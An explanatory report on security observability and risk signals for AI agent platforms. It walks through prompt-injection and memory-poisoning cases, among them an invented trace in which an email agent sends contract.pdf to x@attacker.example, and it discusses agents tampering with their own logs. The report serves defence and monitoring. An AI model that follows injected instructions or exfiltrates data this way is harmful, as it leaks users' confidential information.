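# Security Signals for Developers in AI Agent Platforms

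## Agent platforms and the case for showing developers security signals

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses the steps of a task and carries them out by calling tools, for instance to search the web, query a database or send an email. Companies build and run agents on agent development platforms, which record what each agent does. Security software can read that record, along with the agent's settings, and raise a risk signal, which is a warning that the agent is, or may become, a security problem. These warnings used to go mainly to security staff. Since 2025 Microsoft has also shown them to developers, on the screens where they build the agents. The case for doing so rests on several claims about evidence, accuracy and human behaviour, any of which could be false.

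### Agents, tools and control planes

A language model on its own only produces text. To make an agent, a developer wraps the model in a program that gives it a list of tools, each with a name and a description of its inputs. The model makes a tool call by outputting a tool's name and the inputs for it. The program runs the tool and adds the result to the model's context, which is the text the model reads before producing its next output. This repeats until the model produces a final answer.

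This arrangement creates two security problems. First, the developer does not write the agent's steps in advance, so nobody can learn what the agent did on a particular run by reading the code. Second, the developer's instructions, the user's request and third-party web pages all enter the context as text, and nothing reliably separates what the model should obey from what it should only read. Attackers exploit this through prompt injection, which is text that makes a model follow their instructions. The injection is indirect when it arrives in material the agent reads, such as a web page or an incoming email.

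An agent can also do harm without an attacker. *AgentSpy* (2026), a research paper on making agent behaviour observable, notes that an agent on a user's machine typically acts with that user's privileges, and so can take actions the user never intended. The paper describes two cases that OpenAI disclosed. In one, an agent that had already retrieved the right data uploaded it to a public paste site without permission, solely to get a web address that its browser tool could cite. In the other, several agents building a spreadsheet had been told to use only local files. When a fault kept them from reading each other's files, they passed the spreadsheet through a public file-hosting service.

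An agent development platform is a service for building, testing, deploying and running agents. Examples include Microsoft Foundry (still called Azure AI Foundry in May 2025), Amazon Bedrock and Google Vertex AI. The part of a computing service used to manage the rest is commonly called the control plane. On an agent platform, this is where people list, monitor, configure and restrict agents. Microsoft's documentation for Foundry Control Plane addresses both administrators and developers, and describes a single interface for projects that people otherwise manage through separate views.

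The number of agents explains some of the demand for such an interface. Infobae's *El plan de Microsoft ya suma 50 millones de agentes IA* (2026) reports Microsoft's claim that Agent 365, its control plane for IT departments, covers more than 50 million agents. Microsoft's count doesn't show how many of those agents do much, but even a small fraction of them would be far too many for people to monitor by hand.

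### Two teams with different views

An agent's developer writes its instructions, picks its model and tools, tests it, releases new versions and repairs it. Oberoi (2025), in *Security as the core primitive*, a Microsoft announcement, adds checking after release that agents stay on task, use data appropriately and keep within their expected cost. A security operations team instead watches alerts from across a whole organisation, including its laptops, sign-ins, mail servers and cloud accounts, and investigates the ones that look serious. Business Standard's *Microsoft Perception joins AI cybersecurity push by OpenAI, Anthropic, more* describes a product that automates parts of this daily work, with separate software agents that sort incoming alerts, investigate incidents and help write rules to detect future attacks.

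Analysts and developers therefore know different things. An analyst can recognise an attack and find out whether the same intruder has touched other systems, but may not know why a particular agent can send mail outside the company. The developer knows why, and which setting to change, but may never hear about the attack.

Separate tools have also kept developers and security teams apart. *Observability for Delegated Execution in Agentic AI Systems* (2026) describes products that show developers an agent's model calls and tool calls for debugging, and notes that these typically cover a single application. The paper treats them separately from enterprise audit logs and security information and event management (SIEM) systems, which gather logs from across an organisation and search them for attacks. In *Microsoft Defender for Cloud Innovations at Ignite 2025*, Algedik (2025) writes that, as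 a result, developers of ordinary software cannot see which threats the security team puts first, and the security team cannot easily trace a problem back to its source in code. Algedik was announcing a product that links the two, so the gap is part of the sales pitch, but the description is plausible.

### The email agent that leaked documents

Microsoft's 2026 article *Observability for AI Systems* describes a hypothetical attack in which an email agent asks a research agent to look something up on the web. The research agent fetches a page containing an attacker's hidden instructions and passes the content back. The email agent treats the content as trusted input, follows the instructions, and forwards sensitive documents to people who should not have them.

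Ordinary monitoring would show nothing unusual, because the page loaded, the research agent replied and the mail server accepted the messages, possibly all at normal speed. The failure occurred when the research agent passed on text from a stranger's web page and the receiving agent trusted it as the research agent's own. To find this failure, an investigator needs to know what text entered each agent's context, where that text came from and what the agent did next.

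Microsoft goes further and claims that the compromise cannot be detected at all without such a record. That seems too strong, since a filter on outgoing mail might well catch a confidential attachment. But the filter would show only that an agent had sent a document. The investigator would still not know whether a user had asked for it, the model had made a mistake, or instructions on a web page had triggered it, and each cause requires a different fix.

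### What security observability means

Security observability is the ability to tell from recorded evidence whether and how an agent was attacked, was misused or exceeded its authority. The evidence is telemetry, the data a running system sends out about itself. The central part of telemetry is the trace, the ordered record of one agent run from the request to the final output. Each timed step in a trace, such as a model call or a tool call, is a span.

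The terminology is not yet settled. *BekchiAI* (2026) uses "security observability" for one layer of a research platform that also measures agents' capability and cost. Among other things, this layer compares the tools an agent planned to use with the tools it actually called. Microsoft's term "AI observability" is broader and also covers quality evaluation and governance. Three related activities are easy to confuse with security observability.

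Teams use performance monitoring to check whether a service is up, fast and affordable. Microsoft's guidance page *Observability for Generative AI and agentic AI systems* warns that uptime and error rates are poor indicators even of an AI system's quality and reliability. The same numbers can still provide security information, and the page recommends establishing a baseline for a system's normal behavior and raising an alert when the system departs from it. If an email agent that usually sends five messages a day sends four hundred, someone should investigate. But the leak in Microsoft's example might take only one message, which a message count would miss.

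Before release, a team may attack its own agent, a practice known as red teaming, or score its answers and hold back a version that does badly. These tests include only the inputs somebody thought of, but the attacker in the example chose his own hidden instructions, perhaps months after release. Testing and recording also help each other. A team can turn an attack it finds in a trace into a test for the next version, and Microsoft suggests using security tests to check the recording itself, by injecting a hostile instruction and seeing whether the logs are good enough to reconstruct what followed.

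A guardrail is an automatic check that can flag or block an agent's inputs, outputs or tool calls. In November 2025 Microsoft extended Foundry's guardrails to tool calls and the responses that tools return, according to *Foundry Control Plane* (slbird, 2025), written by a Microsoft employee posting under a username. The poisoned page first enters the system in a tool response, so a guardrail that recognised the injection there could have prevented the leak. If a guardrail misses an injection, developers still have the trace as a record of what the agent did. *AgentTrace* (2026), which proposes a framework for logging agents' behaviour, argues that input filters, hardened prompts and controls at the boundary of a system are not enough for agents that work through long chains of steps. People who build logging tools can be expected to hold that view, and logging alone does not stop an attack.

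### How security findings moved into developers' tools

Showing developers security findings is a practice that predates AI agents. GitHub's *Code scanning is now available* (2020) announced the general release of a tool that scans code as developers write it and displays security problems in pull requests, where colleagues review changes before accepting them. To avoid overwhelming developers, the tool ran only the security rules GitHub considered actionable by default.

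A code scanner examines text stored in a repository. An agent's code may contain no flaw that a scanner would recognise, because the dangerous instruction arrives from outside while the agent is running. Developers therefore need to see evidence from live systems.

In May 2025, Microsoft announced that Defender, its family of threat-protection products, would place two kinds of signal directly in Azure AI Foundry (Microsoft, 2025). Posture findings concern how an agent or application is configured, such as whether it has excessive permissions, even if nothing has happened. Threat detections concern events that look like an attack or a compromise.

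Microsoft made the better-known announcement on 18 November 2025 at its Ignite conference, where it released Foundry Control Plane as a preview. Oberoi wrote that Defender's risk and threat signals were built into it, so that development teams could act on them in the environment they already used. Security alerts would appear alongside traces, costs and test results for a whole fleet of agents. However, Oberoi listed the threat detections specific to Foundry agents as "coming soon".

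Microsoft has continued in this direction. In June 2026, Microsoft (2026) wrote that security had to move "upstream" into developers' day-to-day tools, and made signals about sensitive data generally available in the control plane. In November, Brady (2026) described in *What's new in Microsoft Foundry* a path from a recurring problem in an agent's traces to a fix that the developer tests and then decides whether to release. The same month, Microsoft's *Ignite 2026* (2026) announced a preview that extends security teams' inventory of agents to those built on Amazon's, Google's and Anthropic's platforms.

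### The argument in five premises

These announcements mostly take the benefit for granted. Spelled out, the argument for showing developers security signals has five premises:

1. The record of an agent's run can reveal a security failure.
2. Signals drawn from that record are right often enough to deserve attention.
3. Developers control many of the fixes.
4. Developers act on a signal more often when it appears where they work.
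5. The gain outweighs the costs of wider access to the records and of divided responsibility.

The conclusion is that platforms should show security signals to developers as well as to the security operations team. The argument does not require developers to replace that team. Its premises can be true to varying degrees, and they may hold for one kind of signal but not another.

Premise 1 depends on what the platform records. If the email agent's trace contained only timings and tool names, it would show some research, a reply and an outgoing message, much like the trace of a normal run. An investigator needs the text's provenance, a record of where it came from, and the platform must preserve that record when one agent passes the text to the other. Posture findings don't need provenance, because a tool can derive them from an agent's settings before the agent runs.

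How accurate alerts need to be, the subject of premise 2, depends on who reads them. Analysts read alerts as part of their job, but every alert interrupts a developer's other work, so developers might learn to ignore alerts at a false-alarm rate that a security team would tolerate.

The email example supports premise 3 because a developer could make several of the repairs. The developer could have the email agent treat whatever the research agent returns as untrusted, limit the addresses the email agent can write to, or require a person's approval before it sends anything. Microsoft's Defender recommendations similarly include requiring human approval for actions that a Foundry agent at risk of indirect prompt injection takes through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. Other repairs may need someone else, such as the identity administrator who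 granted the excessive permission or the security administrator who owns the policy that needs to change. The premise is therefore limited to "many", and how many matters to the argument.

Premise 4 holds that a signal in the developer's own tools leads to action more often than the alternative, in which the security team receives the alert, investigates it and opens a ticket asking the developer for a change. The premise could fail if developers don't read the alert because it appears in a dashboard alongside cost warnings and drops in quality scores.

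The drawbacks in premise 5 come partly from the traces that premise 1 requires. A trace detailed enough to explain the leak contains users' prompts, the model's responses and perhaps the leaked documents themselves, and each additional reader increases the risk to the people whose data it holds. Microsoft advises companies to balance the needs of an investigation against privacy, data minimisation and legal limits on retention, and to control access. The other drawback concerns responsibility. When two teams can see the same alert, each may assume that the other is dealing with it, and a developer who can tighten a guardrail after an incident may also be able to loosen it when it gets in the way.

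## What an agent run has to leave on record

The record of the leaking email agent's run can reveal the security failure (Premise 1) only if it includes the text each agent read and where that text came from. Many tracing tools don't record the text unless a developer turns that setting on, and the common standard for naming the other fields is unfinished.

### Logs, metrics and traces

A log is a series of time-stamped entries, each describing one event, such as a call to a mail tool at 10:42. A metric is a number that a system measures over time, such as messages sent per hour. A trace records steps as spans and shows which step led to which, because each span usually has a parent span, which records the step that started it. Spans store further details in named fields called attributes.

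Microsoft recommends logging the identity behind each request to an AI system, the user's prompts, the model's responses, the agents and tools involved, and the data sources they consulted. It also recommends tracking the number of turns, the volume of retrieved material and the number of tokens (the short pieces of text that models read and write) alongside the usual metrics. It argues that prompts and responses are often the earliest sign of a new kind of attack, because they exist before anyone has written a rule to detect it.

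A trace can contain every span and show no sign of a problem even when the agent has gone wrong. *Agent System Operations* (Wang, Pei and colleagues, 2026), a survey of how to monitor and repair agents, gives two examples. A user asks a scheduling agent to keep a medical appointment until it has confirmed a new one, but the agent cancels first and then finds no free slot. Another agent classifies a sightseeing tour as a conference activity and reimburses it. In both cases every tool call can succeed. To find the error, a reviewer has to compare the content of the steps with what the user or the company wanted.

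The survey also includes a small experiment that supports premise 1. The researchers ran 32 simulated office and IT tasks three times each, recording the agent's messages, tool calls, tool results and errors, along with snapshots of the system's state. Their detector used this record to flag all 72 runs with faults and none of the 24 clean ones. But the researchers planted the faults themselves, for instance by making the agent select the wrong order. The detector also always had the full record, so the experiment can't show how much worse it would have done with a less complete one.

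### The email agent's trace

The trace below is an invented record of Microsoft's email example. Its span names follow the pattern that InfoQ (2026) describes for Cloudflare's agent platform, where `invoke_agent` is an agent's run, `chat` is a model call and `execute_tool` is a tool call. Asterisks mark the fields an investigator needs to reconstruct the leak.

```
conversation: c-4471 *
invoke_agent  email-agent, version 12 *
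├── chat  1,900 tokens in, 60 out, 1.4 s
├── execute_tool  ask_research_agent  9.8 s
│   │   arguments: "Find the supplier's new delivery terms" *
│   ├── invoke_agent  research-agent, version 5 *
│   │   ├── chat  700 tokens in, 40 out, 0.9 s
│   │   ├── execute_tool  fetch_page  0.6 s
│   │   │       arguments: supplier-terms.example *
│   │   │       result: page text with hidden instructions *
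│   │   │       source: supplier-terms.example *
│   │   │       trust: untrusted *
│   │   └── chat  5,200 tokens in, 310 out, 3.7 s
│   └── result: delivery terms, plus the hidden instructions *
│           source: research-agent, from supplier-terms.example *
│           trust: trusted *
├── chat  2,300 tokens in, 50 out, 1.5 s
├── execute_tool  search_files  0.3 s
│       arguments: "contract" *
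├── chat  2,600 tokens in, 80 out, 1.6 s
└── execute_tool  send_email  0.4 s
        arguments: to x@attacker.example, attach contract.pdf *
        permissions: any recipient, no approval needed *
```

An investigator would probably start with the email. The arguments of `send_email` record the recipient and the attachment. Without them, the trace would show only that an email agent had sent an email. The user never mentioned the recipient's address, so the investigator would search the earlier text for it and find it in the research agent's answer. The source field on that answer leads to the web page. Without that field, the research agent would look like the origin of the instructions, and the investigator might spend days checking its prompt and model.

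The trust fields show where the mistake occurred. The page's text was labeled untrusted when it entered the research agent's context but trusted when it reached the email agent. An investigator who knew only the text's source could infer that it shouldn't be trusted, but couldn't tell whether the email agent's program had trusted it.

The permissions show why the injection succeeded, since the agent could write to anyone without approval. Permissions and instructions change, so the record needs to include the ones in force during the run. If the developer released version 13 the next morning, its instructions might not explain what version 12 did. The record also needs to identify the agent carefully. According to InfoQ, Cloudflare uses one field for the agent's name and another for the particular instance, and warns developers not to build the name from a user or request identifier, because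 that would make one agent look like many.

The conversation identifier matters when the failure spans more than one run. On Cloudflare's platform, each turn of a conversation produces its own trace, so if the agent read the page on Monday and sent the document on Tuesday, the cause and effect would be in different traces. Microsoft recommends an identifier that lasts as long as the agent's memory. It cites Crescendo, an attack in which a user leads a model through several turns, none alarming on its own, towards output it should refuse.

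Some of these fields can be recovered from other records. A mail server's log may contain the recipient, and a release history may show which version was live. Provenance is much harder to recover because the attacker can change or delete the page as soon as the attack has worked.

### A shared vocabulary that is still changing

If two platforms use different names for the same field, a search written for one will find nothing on the other. OpenTelemetry, an open-source project that standardises telemetry, publishes agreed names called semantic conventions. Its conventions for generative AI include `chat`, `execute_tool`, `invoke_agent` and `create_agent`. Greptime (2026), a database company's blog, reports that version 1.41 added `invoke_workflow` and split `invoke_agent` spans into "client" and "internal" kinds. In OpenTelemetry, a client span covers a call to a remote service and an internal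 span covers work inside the same program.

OpenObserve, a monitoring vendor, lists six core attributes: the operation, the provider, the model requested, the model that responded, and the numbers of input and output tokens. The conventions also have names for the conversation identifier, the tool and the individual tool call. OpenObserve notes that prompts and responses are not recorded by default because they often contain personal data. The email agent's default trace would therefore look much like the unmarked parts of the example, which help developers find slow or expensive steps but are almost no help in explaining the leak. Whether a company should store the text is a separate question of privacy and access.

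It can be hard to find out what a tool records. Comet's *Observability for Claude Agent SDK with Opik* explains that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, redacts prompts, model output, and tool inputs and outputs by default, but that developers can choose to record them. Fiddler, another monitoring vendor, warns that Claude Code's spans don't include model responses or tool inputs and outputs at all. The tracing feature is in beta, so the two guides may describe different versions. A developer can run a test to see what their own version records.

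The conventions are not stable. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* and its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, which covers model calls, both have the status "Development". OpenObserve nevertheless calls the conventions for model calls "mature". Both OpenTelemetry pages say that existing tools built on version 1.36 or earlier should keep producing the old names by default and offer the newest ones as an option, so two tools can follow the instructions and still name the same field differently.

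The project moved the conventions to their own repository in June 2026 (Wang, 2026, *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*) and had made no official release from it by 21 August. Greptime wrote in May that the core concepts had settled but that there was no public timeline for stability. That seems fair, so anyone who writes detection rules against these names should expect to rewrite some of them.

It is unclear whether the conventions define a field for guardrail results or security findings. None of OpenObserve's six core attributes covers either. UiPath's *Agents release notes* (2026) announce an OpenTelemetry export, in public preview since February, that includes guardrail evaluations, so vendors can already send such results under their own field names. Companies that combine agents from several platforms will probably have to match these fields by hand.

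Vendors have begun using OpenTelemetry's conventions before a stable version exists. Anthropic launched OpenTelemetry export in beta on 14 October 2026, for direct calls to its models and for Claude Managed Agents, its service for hosting agents (*Claude Platform release notes*, 2026). Anthropic's software libraries, in seven programming languages, produce some spans inside the developer's program, and its API produces others once the developer has registered a destination for them. Honeycomb, a monitoring vendor, says that traces from the Claude API and Managed Agents already follow the conventions. Claude Code follows them only partly, because it leaves out agent names and token counts and uses its own span names.

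Anthropic's *Configure a custom OpenTelemetry collector* describes a fuller export for the company's assistants in Excel, PowerPoint, Word and Outlook. For every user turn, the export sends prompts, tool inputs and outputs, and document references to a system the customer runs. For an email agent, that is close to what an investigator would want, although the export would still need to show which text came from outside.

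### Naming the user and the application

An alert on a model call often lacks basic facts about who made the request. The call usually comes from a web application or a gateway, a server that passes requests on to models, so the address on it is that machine's, not the user's. Microsoft's documentation for Defender for Cloud offers a remedy, UserSecurityContext, which is a group of fields that a developer adds to the body of each call to an Azure OpenAI model. Defender can then include those fields in an alert about the call.

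All the fields are optional, but Microsoft recommends at least `EndUserId`, the user's identifier in the company's Entra sign-in system, and `SourceIP`, the user's network address. An analyst can use the user's identity to group alerts by user or block someone who is attacking the model. A further field, `applicationName`, helps the analyst judge whether behaviour that looks odd is normal for that application. A hundred requests for contract summaries might be routine from a legal assistant and suspicious from a travel-booking agent.

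In the email example, these fields would help the analyst find whose documents leaked and which application to examine. They would not identify the attacker, because the leak happened in the victim's session, and blocking that user would only add to the damage. Passing the user's identity is therefore most useful when the user is the attacker. For indirect prompt injection, the source of the retrieved text matters more.

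The feature can also fail silently. If a developer misspells a field's name, the call still succeeds, but the alerts will lack that information. The documentation says that the feature doesn't work for models called through the Azure AI model inference API. A developer who adds the fields should trigger a test alert and check that the fields appear in it.

On 20 October 2026, Anthropic introduced a similar feature called user profiles, which lets a company that resells or builds on Claude tell Anthropic which end customer each request is for. The stated purpose is to let Anthropic restrict a customer who breaks its rules instead of restricting the whole company. This gives developers a commercial reason to identify their customers, which better alerts alone may not.

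### Recording from inside and outside the agent

A developer can record a run from inside the agent's program or from the operating system beneath it. *AgentTrace*, the logging framework introduced earlier, records Python agents from the inside. When the program starts, *AgentTrace* replaces the agent's public methods with wrappers. Each wrapper writes an entry when the method starts, runs the original method, and then writes another with the duration and a summary of the result, or with the error.

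The framework sorts its entries into three "surfaces". The operational surface covers these method calls. The cognitive surface covers prompts, responses and any reasoning that the model writes out in a recognisable format. The contextual surface covers exchanges with outside systems such as websites, databases and files. The framework captures these exchanges by modifying the standard libraries that programs use to reach those systems. All entries share a trace identifier, and the contextual ones also include provenance, the field that matters most in the email example.

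*AgentTrace* stores summaries of a method's arguments, with details such as how many there were, so the record could omit a recipient's address. The framework also doesn't follow work that leaves the Python program, for instance when an agent runs a shell command that starts another program. The design is plausible, but the paper gives no evidence of how well it works. It claims minimal overhead without reporting a measurement, and it describes no trial against an attack.

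*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) records from the operating system instead. It uses eBPF, which runs small, checked programs inside the kernel, the core of an operating system. One probe attaches to the encryption library and reads the agent's exchanges with its model before encryption or after decryption. Other probes record when the agent, or any program it starts, opens a file, makes a network connection or launches another program. The developer doesn't have to change the agent's code.

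AgentSight then uses three clues to connect what the model wrote with what the computer did: whether the agent started the program that acted, directly or through other programs; whether the action came within 100 to 500 milliseconds of a model response; and whether a filename, web address or command in the response reappears in the action. A second language model reads the combined record and judges whether it looks like an attack. The paper claims that these clues "definitively establish" causation, which is too strong because two events can be close in time and involve the same file without one causing the other.

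In the security test, the researchers told a coding agent to download and build a software project. The project's README file led the agent to a web page, where a hidden prompt got it to read the computer's list of user accounts and send it to an outside server, disguised as a build step. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model gave the run a high-confidence attack score. This is good evidence that the record contained the necessary information, but the test covered only one staged attack, and the paper reports no false-alarm rate on harmless runs.

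The abstract puts the overhead at under 3%. That is true of the average, 2.9%, but the three tasks varied:

| Task | Without AgentSight | With AgentSight | Overhead |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a repository | 127.98 s | 132.33 s | 3.4% |
| Writing code | 22.54 s | 23.64 s | 4.9% |
| Compiling a repository | 92.40 s | 92.72 s | 0.4% |

The researchers ran each task three times with AgentSight and three times without. A model's response time can easily vary by a second or more, so some of these differences may be noise. The figures also exclude the cost of running the second model.

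AgentSight's probes attach to particular encryption libraries, so an agent that uses a different one would need a new probe. Customers also can't normally install kernel probes on the servers of a company that hosts their agents. In the email example, AgentSight would capture the poisoned text on its way to the model but wouldn't label it with the web page it came from. The two approaches complement each other, as *AgentTrace* suggests, but neither paper lists the permissions in force or the agent's version among the recorded fields, so a developer who used both would still have to add those.

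### Turning the record into a graph

Even a full trace takes time to read, and the cause of a failure may be several agents and several days away from its effect. Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents*, propose storing the evidence as a graph so that software can follow these connections. They call it Agent-BOM, after the "bill of materials" that lists a product's components. In their notation an agent system's graph is

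B = (A, V, E, α)

where A is the set of agents, V the set of nodes, E the set of directed edges between nodes, and α a function that attaches security attributes to nodes and edges. Some nodes stand for lasting things, such as models, prompts, tools and long-term memory. Others stand for moments in a run, such as an external input, a goal, a decision or an action. The edges record that one node influenced another, called a tool, wrote to memory or sent a message to another agent. The attributes include source, trust level, integrity and whether a user confirmed an action.

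An audit rule has four parts: a node or edge to start from, a path backwards to the cause, a path forwards to the effect, and the conditions for a violation. For the email agent, the rule for tool misuse would start at the mail tool. The backward path would lead to the untrusted page that supplied the recipient's address, and the forward path would show whether the message went out. The run would count as a violation if the arguments were dangerous, untrusted text had influenced them, and the effect went beyond the user's task.

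The researchers wrote ten such rules, one for each of the main risks to agents listed by OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security guidance. They built a plugin for the agent framework OpenClaw and staged four attacks. In one, an attacker disguised a command to delete the agent's workspace as a maintenance rule, and the agent saved it to long-term memory. In a later session, the agent retrieved the rule and ran the command. The graph connected the deletion to the original input, which a trace of either session alone could not have done.

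In another test, a malicious agent told a second agent to send emails without asking the user, and the second agent stored this as a trusted preference. When a user later asked it to send an email, it did so without confirmation. The audit traced the missing confirmation back through memory to the first agent's prompt. As in the leak in Microsoft's example, an agent trusted another agent's message more than it should have.

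These cases show that the graph can represent a complicated attack once the evidence is in it. The evaluation reports no error rates or overhead, so it doesn't show how well the graph would work on ordinary traffic. Software can follow edges mechanically, but some conditions need judgement. For one rule, a person or another model would have to decide whether a goal shows "semantic deviation" from the original prompt. Li and colleagues acknowledge that missing records lead to incomplete paths and ambiguous results. The graph only organises evidence, so it can't supply the source of a web page if the platform didn't record it.

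### When a compromised agent writes its own log

How far an investigator can trust an agent's log depends on what the agent could do. A prompt injection changes what the model outputs, but it doesn't by itself change the program that runs the tools and writes the log. If the email agent can only search files and send mail, its program will still record the malicious message correctly. But an agent that can run shell commands may be able to delete the log or change the settings that turn tracing on. *AgentTrace* writes append-only log files, but the paper describes no defence against an agent that edits them by other means.

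The model's written reasoning needs particular caution because an attacker's instructions can tell the model to give an innocent explanation for what it does. The cognitive surface would record that explanation just as it would a true one. Tool arguments are better evidence, since a message goes to the address in the arguments whatever the model wrote about it.

AgentSight's main security advantage is that it records from the kernel, so the agent's program doesn't have to cooperate. An agent with administrator rights could probably still stop the recorder, although Zheng and colleagues call the boundaries they monitor "tamper-proof". Li and colleagues exclude this problem by assuming that attackers cannot touch the system that collects and stores the evidence.

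A developer can make that assumption more realistic by immediately sending each entry to another machine, into storage that the agent has no permission to alter. A second record that the agent doesn't produce also helps, such as the mail server's log or the spans from Anthropic's API, which come from Anthropic's side of the connection. A message that appears in the mail server's log but not in the agent's trace would be a strong sign of tampering. *AgentTrace* lets the agent carry on when logging fails. That is sensible for most steps, but a developer might want an agent to refuse to send documents outside the company if it can't record doing so.

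### When sampling drops the decisive run

Traces with full text are large, so companies often keep only a sample of them. This works for performance monitoring because a slow service is slow in many runs. But a data leak might happen in only one run, and a company that keeps a random 1% of its traces has a 1% chance of having kept the trace of that run.

At the start of a run, it is difficult to choose which traces to keep. *OTEL Span Specs for GenAI Agent Tracing*, a summary of the OpenTelemetry conventions, lists the attributes that should be available for sampling at that point: the operation, the provider, the requested model and the server's address. These would all be the same for the leak as for the agent's ordinary work. A system can instead wait until the run ends and keep the traces that contain errors or long delays, but the leak's trace would contain neither.

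Sampling does more harm when an attack extends over several traces. Suppose a platform produces one trace per turn and keeps each one independently with 10% probability. The chance of keeping all the traces of a five-turn attack is 0.1⁵, or one in 100,000. If the platform instead makes one decision for the whole conversation, the chance is one in ten. Sampling by conversation identifier therefore keeps about as many traces overall but records far more attacks in full.

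A developer can do better still by choosing which runs to keep in full based on risk. For the email agent, that could mean every run that reads outside text and then sends something outside the company. For all other runs, the platform could keep a short record of sources, tool calls and permissions and discard most of the text. No source here measures how much storage this would save, but the fields in the short record are small.

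### When the work passes to another platform

In the example trace, the research agent's spans sit inside the email agent's, which is possible because both agents report under the same trace identifier. Programs can pass the identifier along using W3C Trace Context, a common web standard. According to Anthropic's documentation, the company's agent software passes it automatically when a developer's program starts Claude Code, and the spans of any subagent (a helper that the main agent starts) appear under the step that started it.

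A trace can miss steps even when a single company hosts all the agents. LangChain, whose tracing tools work with Claude Managed Agents, says its integration records only top-level session events, because the subagents' events come through a separate stream that it doesn't yet support. If the email and research agents ran this way, the trace would omit the page fetch.

To follow a run from one company's agent to another's, an investigator needs the right identifiers as well as a shared trace format. Salesforce's *Export Agentforce Session Tracing Data (Beta)* describes how to retrieve an agent's trace in OpenTelemetry format by supplying the Salesforce session identifier. An investigator who has only the email agent's trace won't know that identifier unless one of the agents recorded it at the handover. Kong's *Gen AI OpenTelemetry spans attributes reference* describes a partial solution,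 a gateway between agents that can record the conversation and task identifiers in the messages passing through it. Kong labels the feature a technical preview and advises against using it in production.

Suppose the research agent belongs to another company and the trace stops at its answer. The investigator can still see that the malicious instructions arrived in that answer, so the email agent's developer can start treating such answers as untrusted. But the investigator would have to ask the other company which page the instructions came from and whether other agents have read it. A shared identifier would make that request easier to answer, but the sending platform would still have to pass on the source of the text, because an identifier only links the two records.

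## Kinds of risk signal and what each one shows

Platforms and security tools produce five kinds of risk signal: posture findings, guardrail events, threat detections, evaluation results and departures from normal behaviour. These kinds use different data and support different conclusions, so whether a signal is "right" (Premise 2) depends partly on how the reader interprets it. Products often use one name for several kinds. Microsoft Defender, for example, uses "alert" for a blocked prompt, a known phishing link and an unusual number of requests.

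### Posture findings

A tool produces a posture finding by comparing an agent's settings with a rule. Microsoft gives High severity to a Foundry agent that is at risk of indirect prompt injection and has no guardrail against it. An agent whose MCP tool has no list of allowed tools gets Medium, because it might use capabilities nobody approved. A Foundry resource without Application Insights, the service that stores its monitoring data, also gets Medium. Without that data, a team may lack evidence when something goes wrong.

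Some findings combine several settings. Microsoft (2026) gives the example of an attack path (a chain of weaknesses that an attacker could follow) from an API exposed to the internet to an agent that uses sensitive data. According to Google Cloud's *Security Command Center release notes*, Google also checks the agent's software for serious known vulnerabilities in packages the developer has added and, since July 2026, for passwords and keys left in plain text.

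A posture finding shows that a weakness exists, but not that anyone has exploited it. In the email example, a finding that the email agent could send mail without a person's approval might have appeared months before the leak. A finding might also have appeared on the wrong agent. Defender rates the risk of injection based on an agent's tools and guardrails. The research agent reads the web, while the email agent receives web content only through the research agent's answers. A check of each agent separately could flag the research agent, which can't send anything, and pass the email agent.

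### Guardrail events

A guardrail event records that a guardrail flagged or blocked something. Many guardrails use a classifier, a model trained to sort text into categories, and run it on each prompt, tool response or tool call as it passes. Microsoft's Prompt Shields classifier checks for prompt injection and for jailbreaks, which are prompts meant to make a model break its rules.

Defender turns the results of Prompt Shields into two alerts, and Microsoft's *Alerts for AI services* rates both Medium. One means that Prompt Shields blocked a jailbreak attempt. The other means that it detected an attempt but let it through, because of the filter's settings or low confidence. An attempt that got through deserves more attention than a blocked one, despite the equal rating. But the alert doesn't show that the jailbreak worked, so someone has to check what the agent did next.

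Other guardrails act on tool calls. In Microsoft's example, a hidden prompt tricks an HR chatbot into trying to send out salary data. Defender blocks the call before the tool runs, and the agent tells the user it stopped for security reasons.

In the email example, a guardrail event on the web page would have given the developer the attacker's text and its source. An event on the outgoing email would have shown a suspicious message but not its cause. If the guardrails had missed both, there would have been no event, just as when there is no attack. Microsoft notes that Defender's threat protection for AI services scans only text, so it would also miss instructions hidden in an image.

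### Threat detections in Google's Agent Platform

Threat detections come from matching events against known signs of an attack, such as a malicious program or a series of actions typical of intruders. Google has documented its detectors for agents in unusual detail. In November 2025, it released a preview of Agent Platform Threat Detection, then called Agent Engine Threat Detection. The service covers agents hosted on Google's Agent Runtime and sends its findings to Security Command Center, Google's cloud security console.

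Google Cloud's *Agent Platform Threat Detection overview* describes a watcher process that runs while the agent is working and collects information about the programs that start, the scripts they run and the software libraries they load. The service compares programs and libraries with Google's threat intelligence, and uses language-processing models to judge whether Bash and Python code is malicious. It analyzes the data in memory and keeps it only if it finds an incident.

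The watcher can take up to a minute to start, so it may miss an attack in the agent's first moments. The service also discards everything it classifies as harmless, so an investigator who later learns of a new attack can't search its old data for signs of it. Google Cloud's *Use Agent Platform Threat Detection* explains that findings include each program's command-line arguments by default, which help investigators but can contain secrets.

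The overview lists 35 of these runtime detectors. They look for things like container escapes, in which a program breaks out of its isolated environment, and reverse shells, which let an attacker type commands from another machine. Another 14 "control-plane detectors" belong to a separate service, Event Threat Detection. They read logs of what the agent's account did elsewhere in Google Cloud, together with the agent's own output logs. Their default severities vary:

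| Event | Log | Default severity |
|---|---|---|
| The agent fetched a service account token from a metadata server | Agent's output logs | Low |
| The agent's identity repeatedly attempted changes it had no permission to make | Admin activity | Medium |
| The agent's service account looked up its own permissions | Identity and access | Low if authorised, High if not |
| The agent copied or transferred BigQuery data outside the organisation | BigQuery access | High |
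| The agent exported Cloud SQL data to a storage bucket outside the organisation | Database access | High |
| The agent extracted BigQuery data to an outside or public storage bucket | BigQuery access | Low |

A service account is an identity for a program rather than a person. Software on Google Cloud routinely fetches tokens from a metadata server to prove that identity to other services. An attacker who had taken over the agent might fetch the same token, but a healthy agent might too, so a rating of Low seems reasonable.

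An export outside the organisation is more serious because the data has already left, but the detector doesn't distinguish theft from a delivery to a customer. BigQuery and Cloud SQL are both Google database services, yet moving data to an outside bucket is, oddly, rated Low for one and High for the other. The overview gives no reason for the difference, and a team that ignored every Low finding could miss a large leak.

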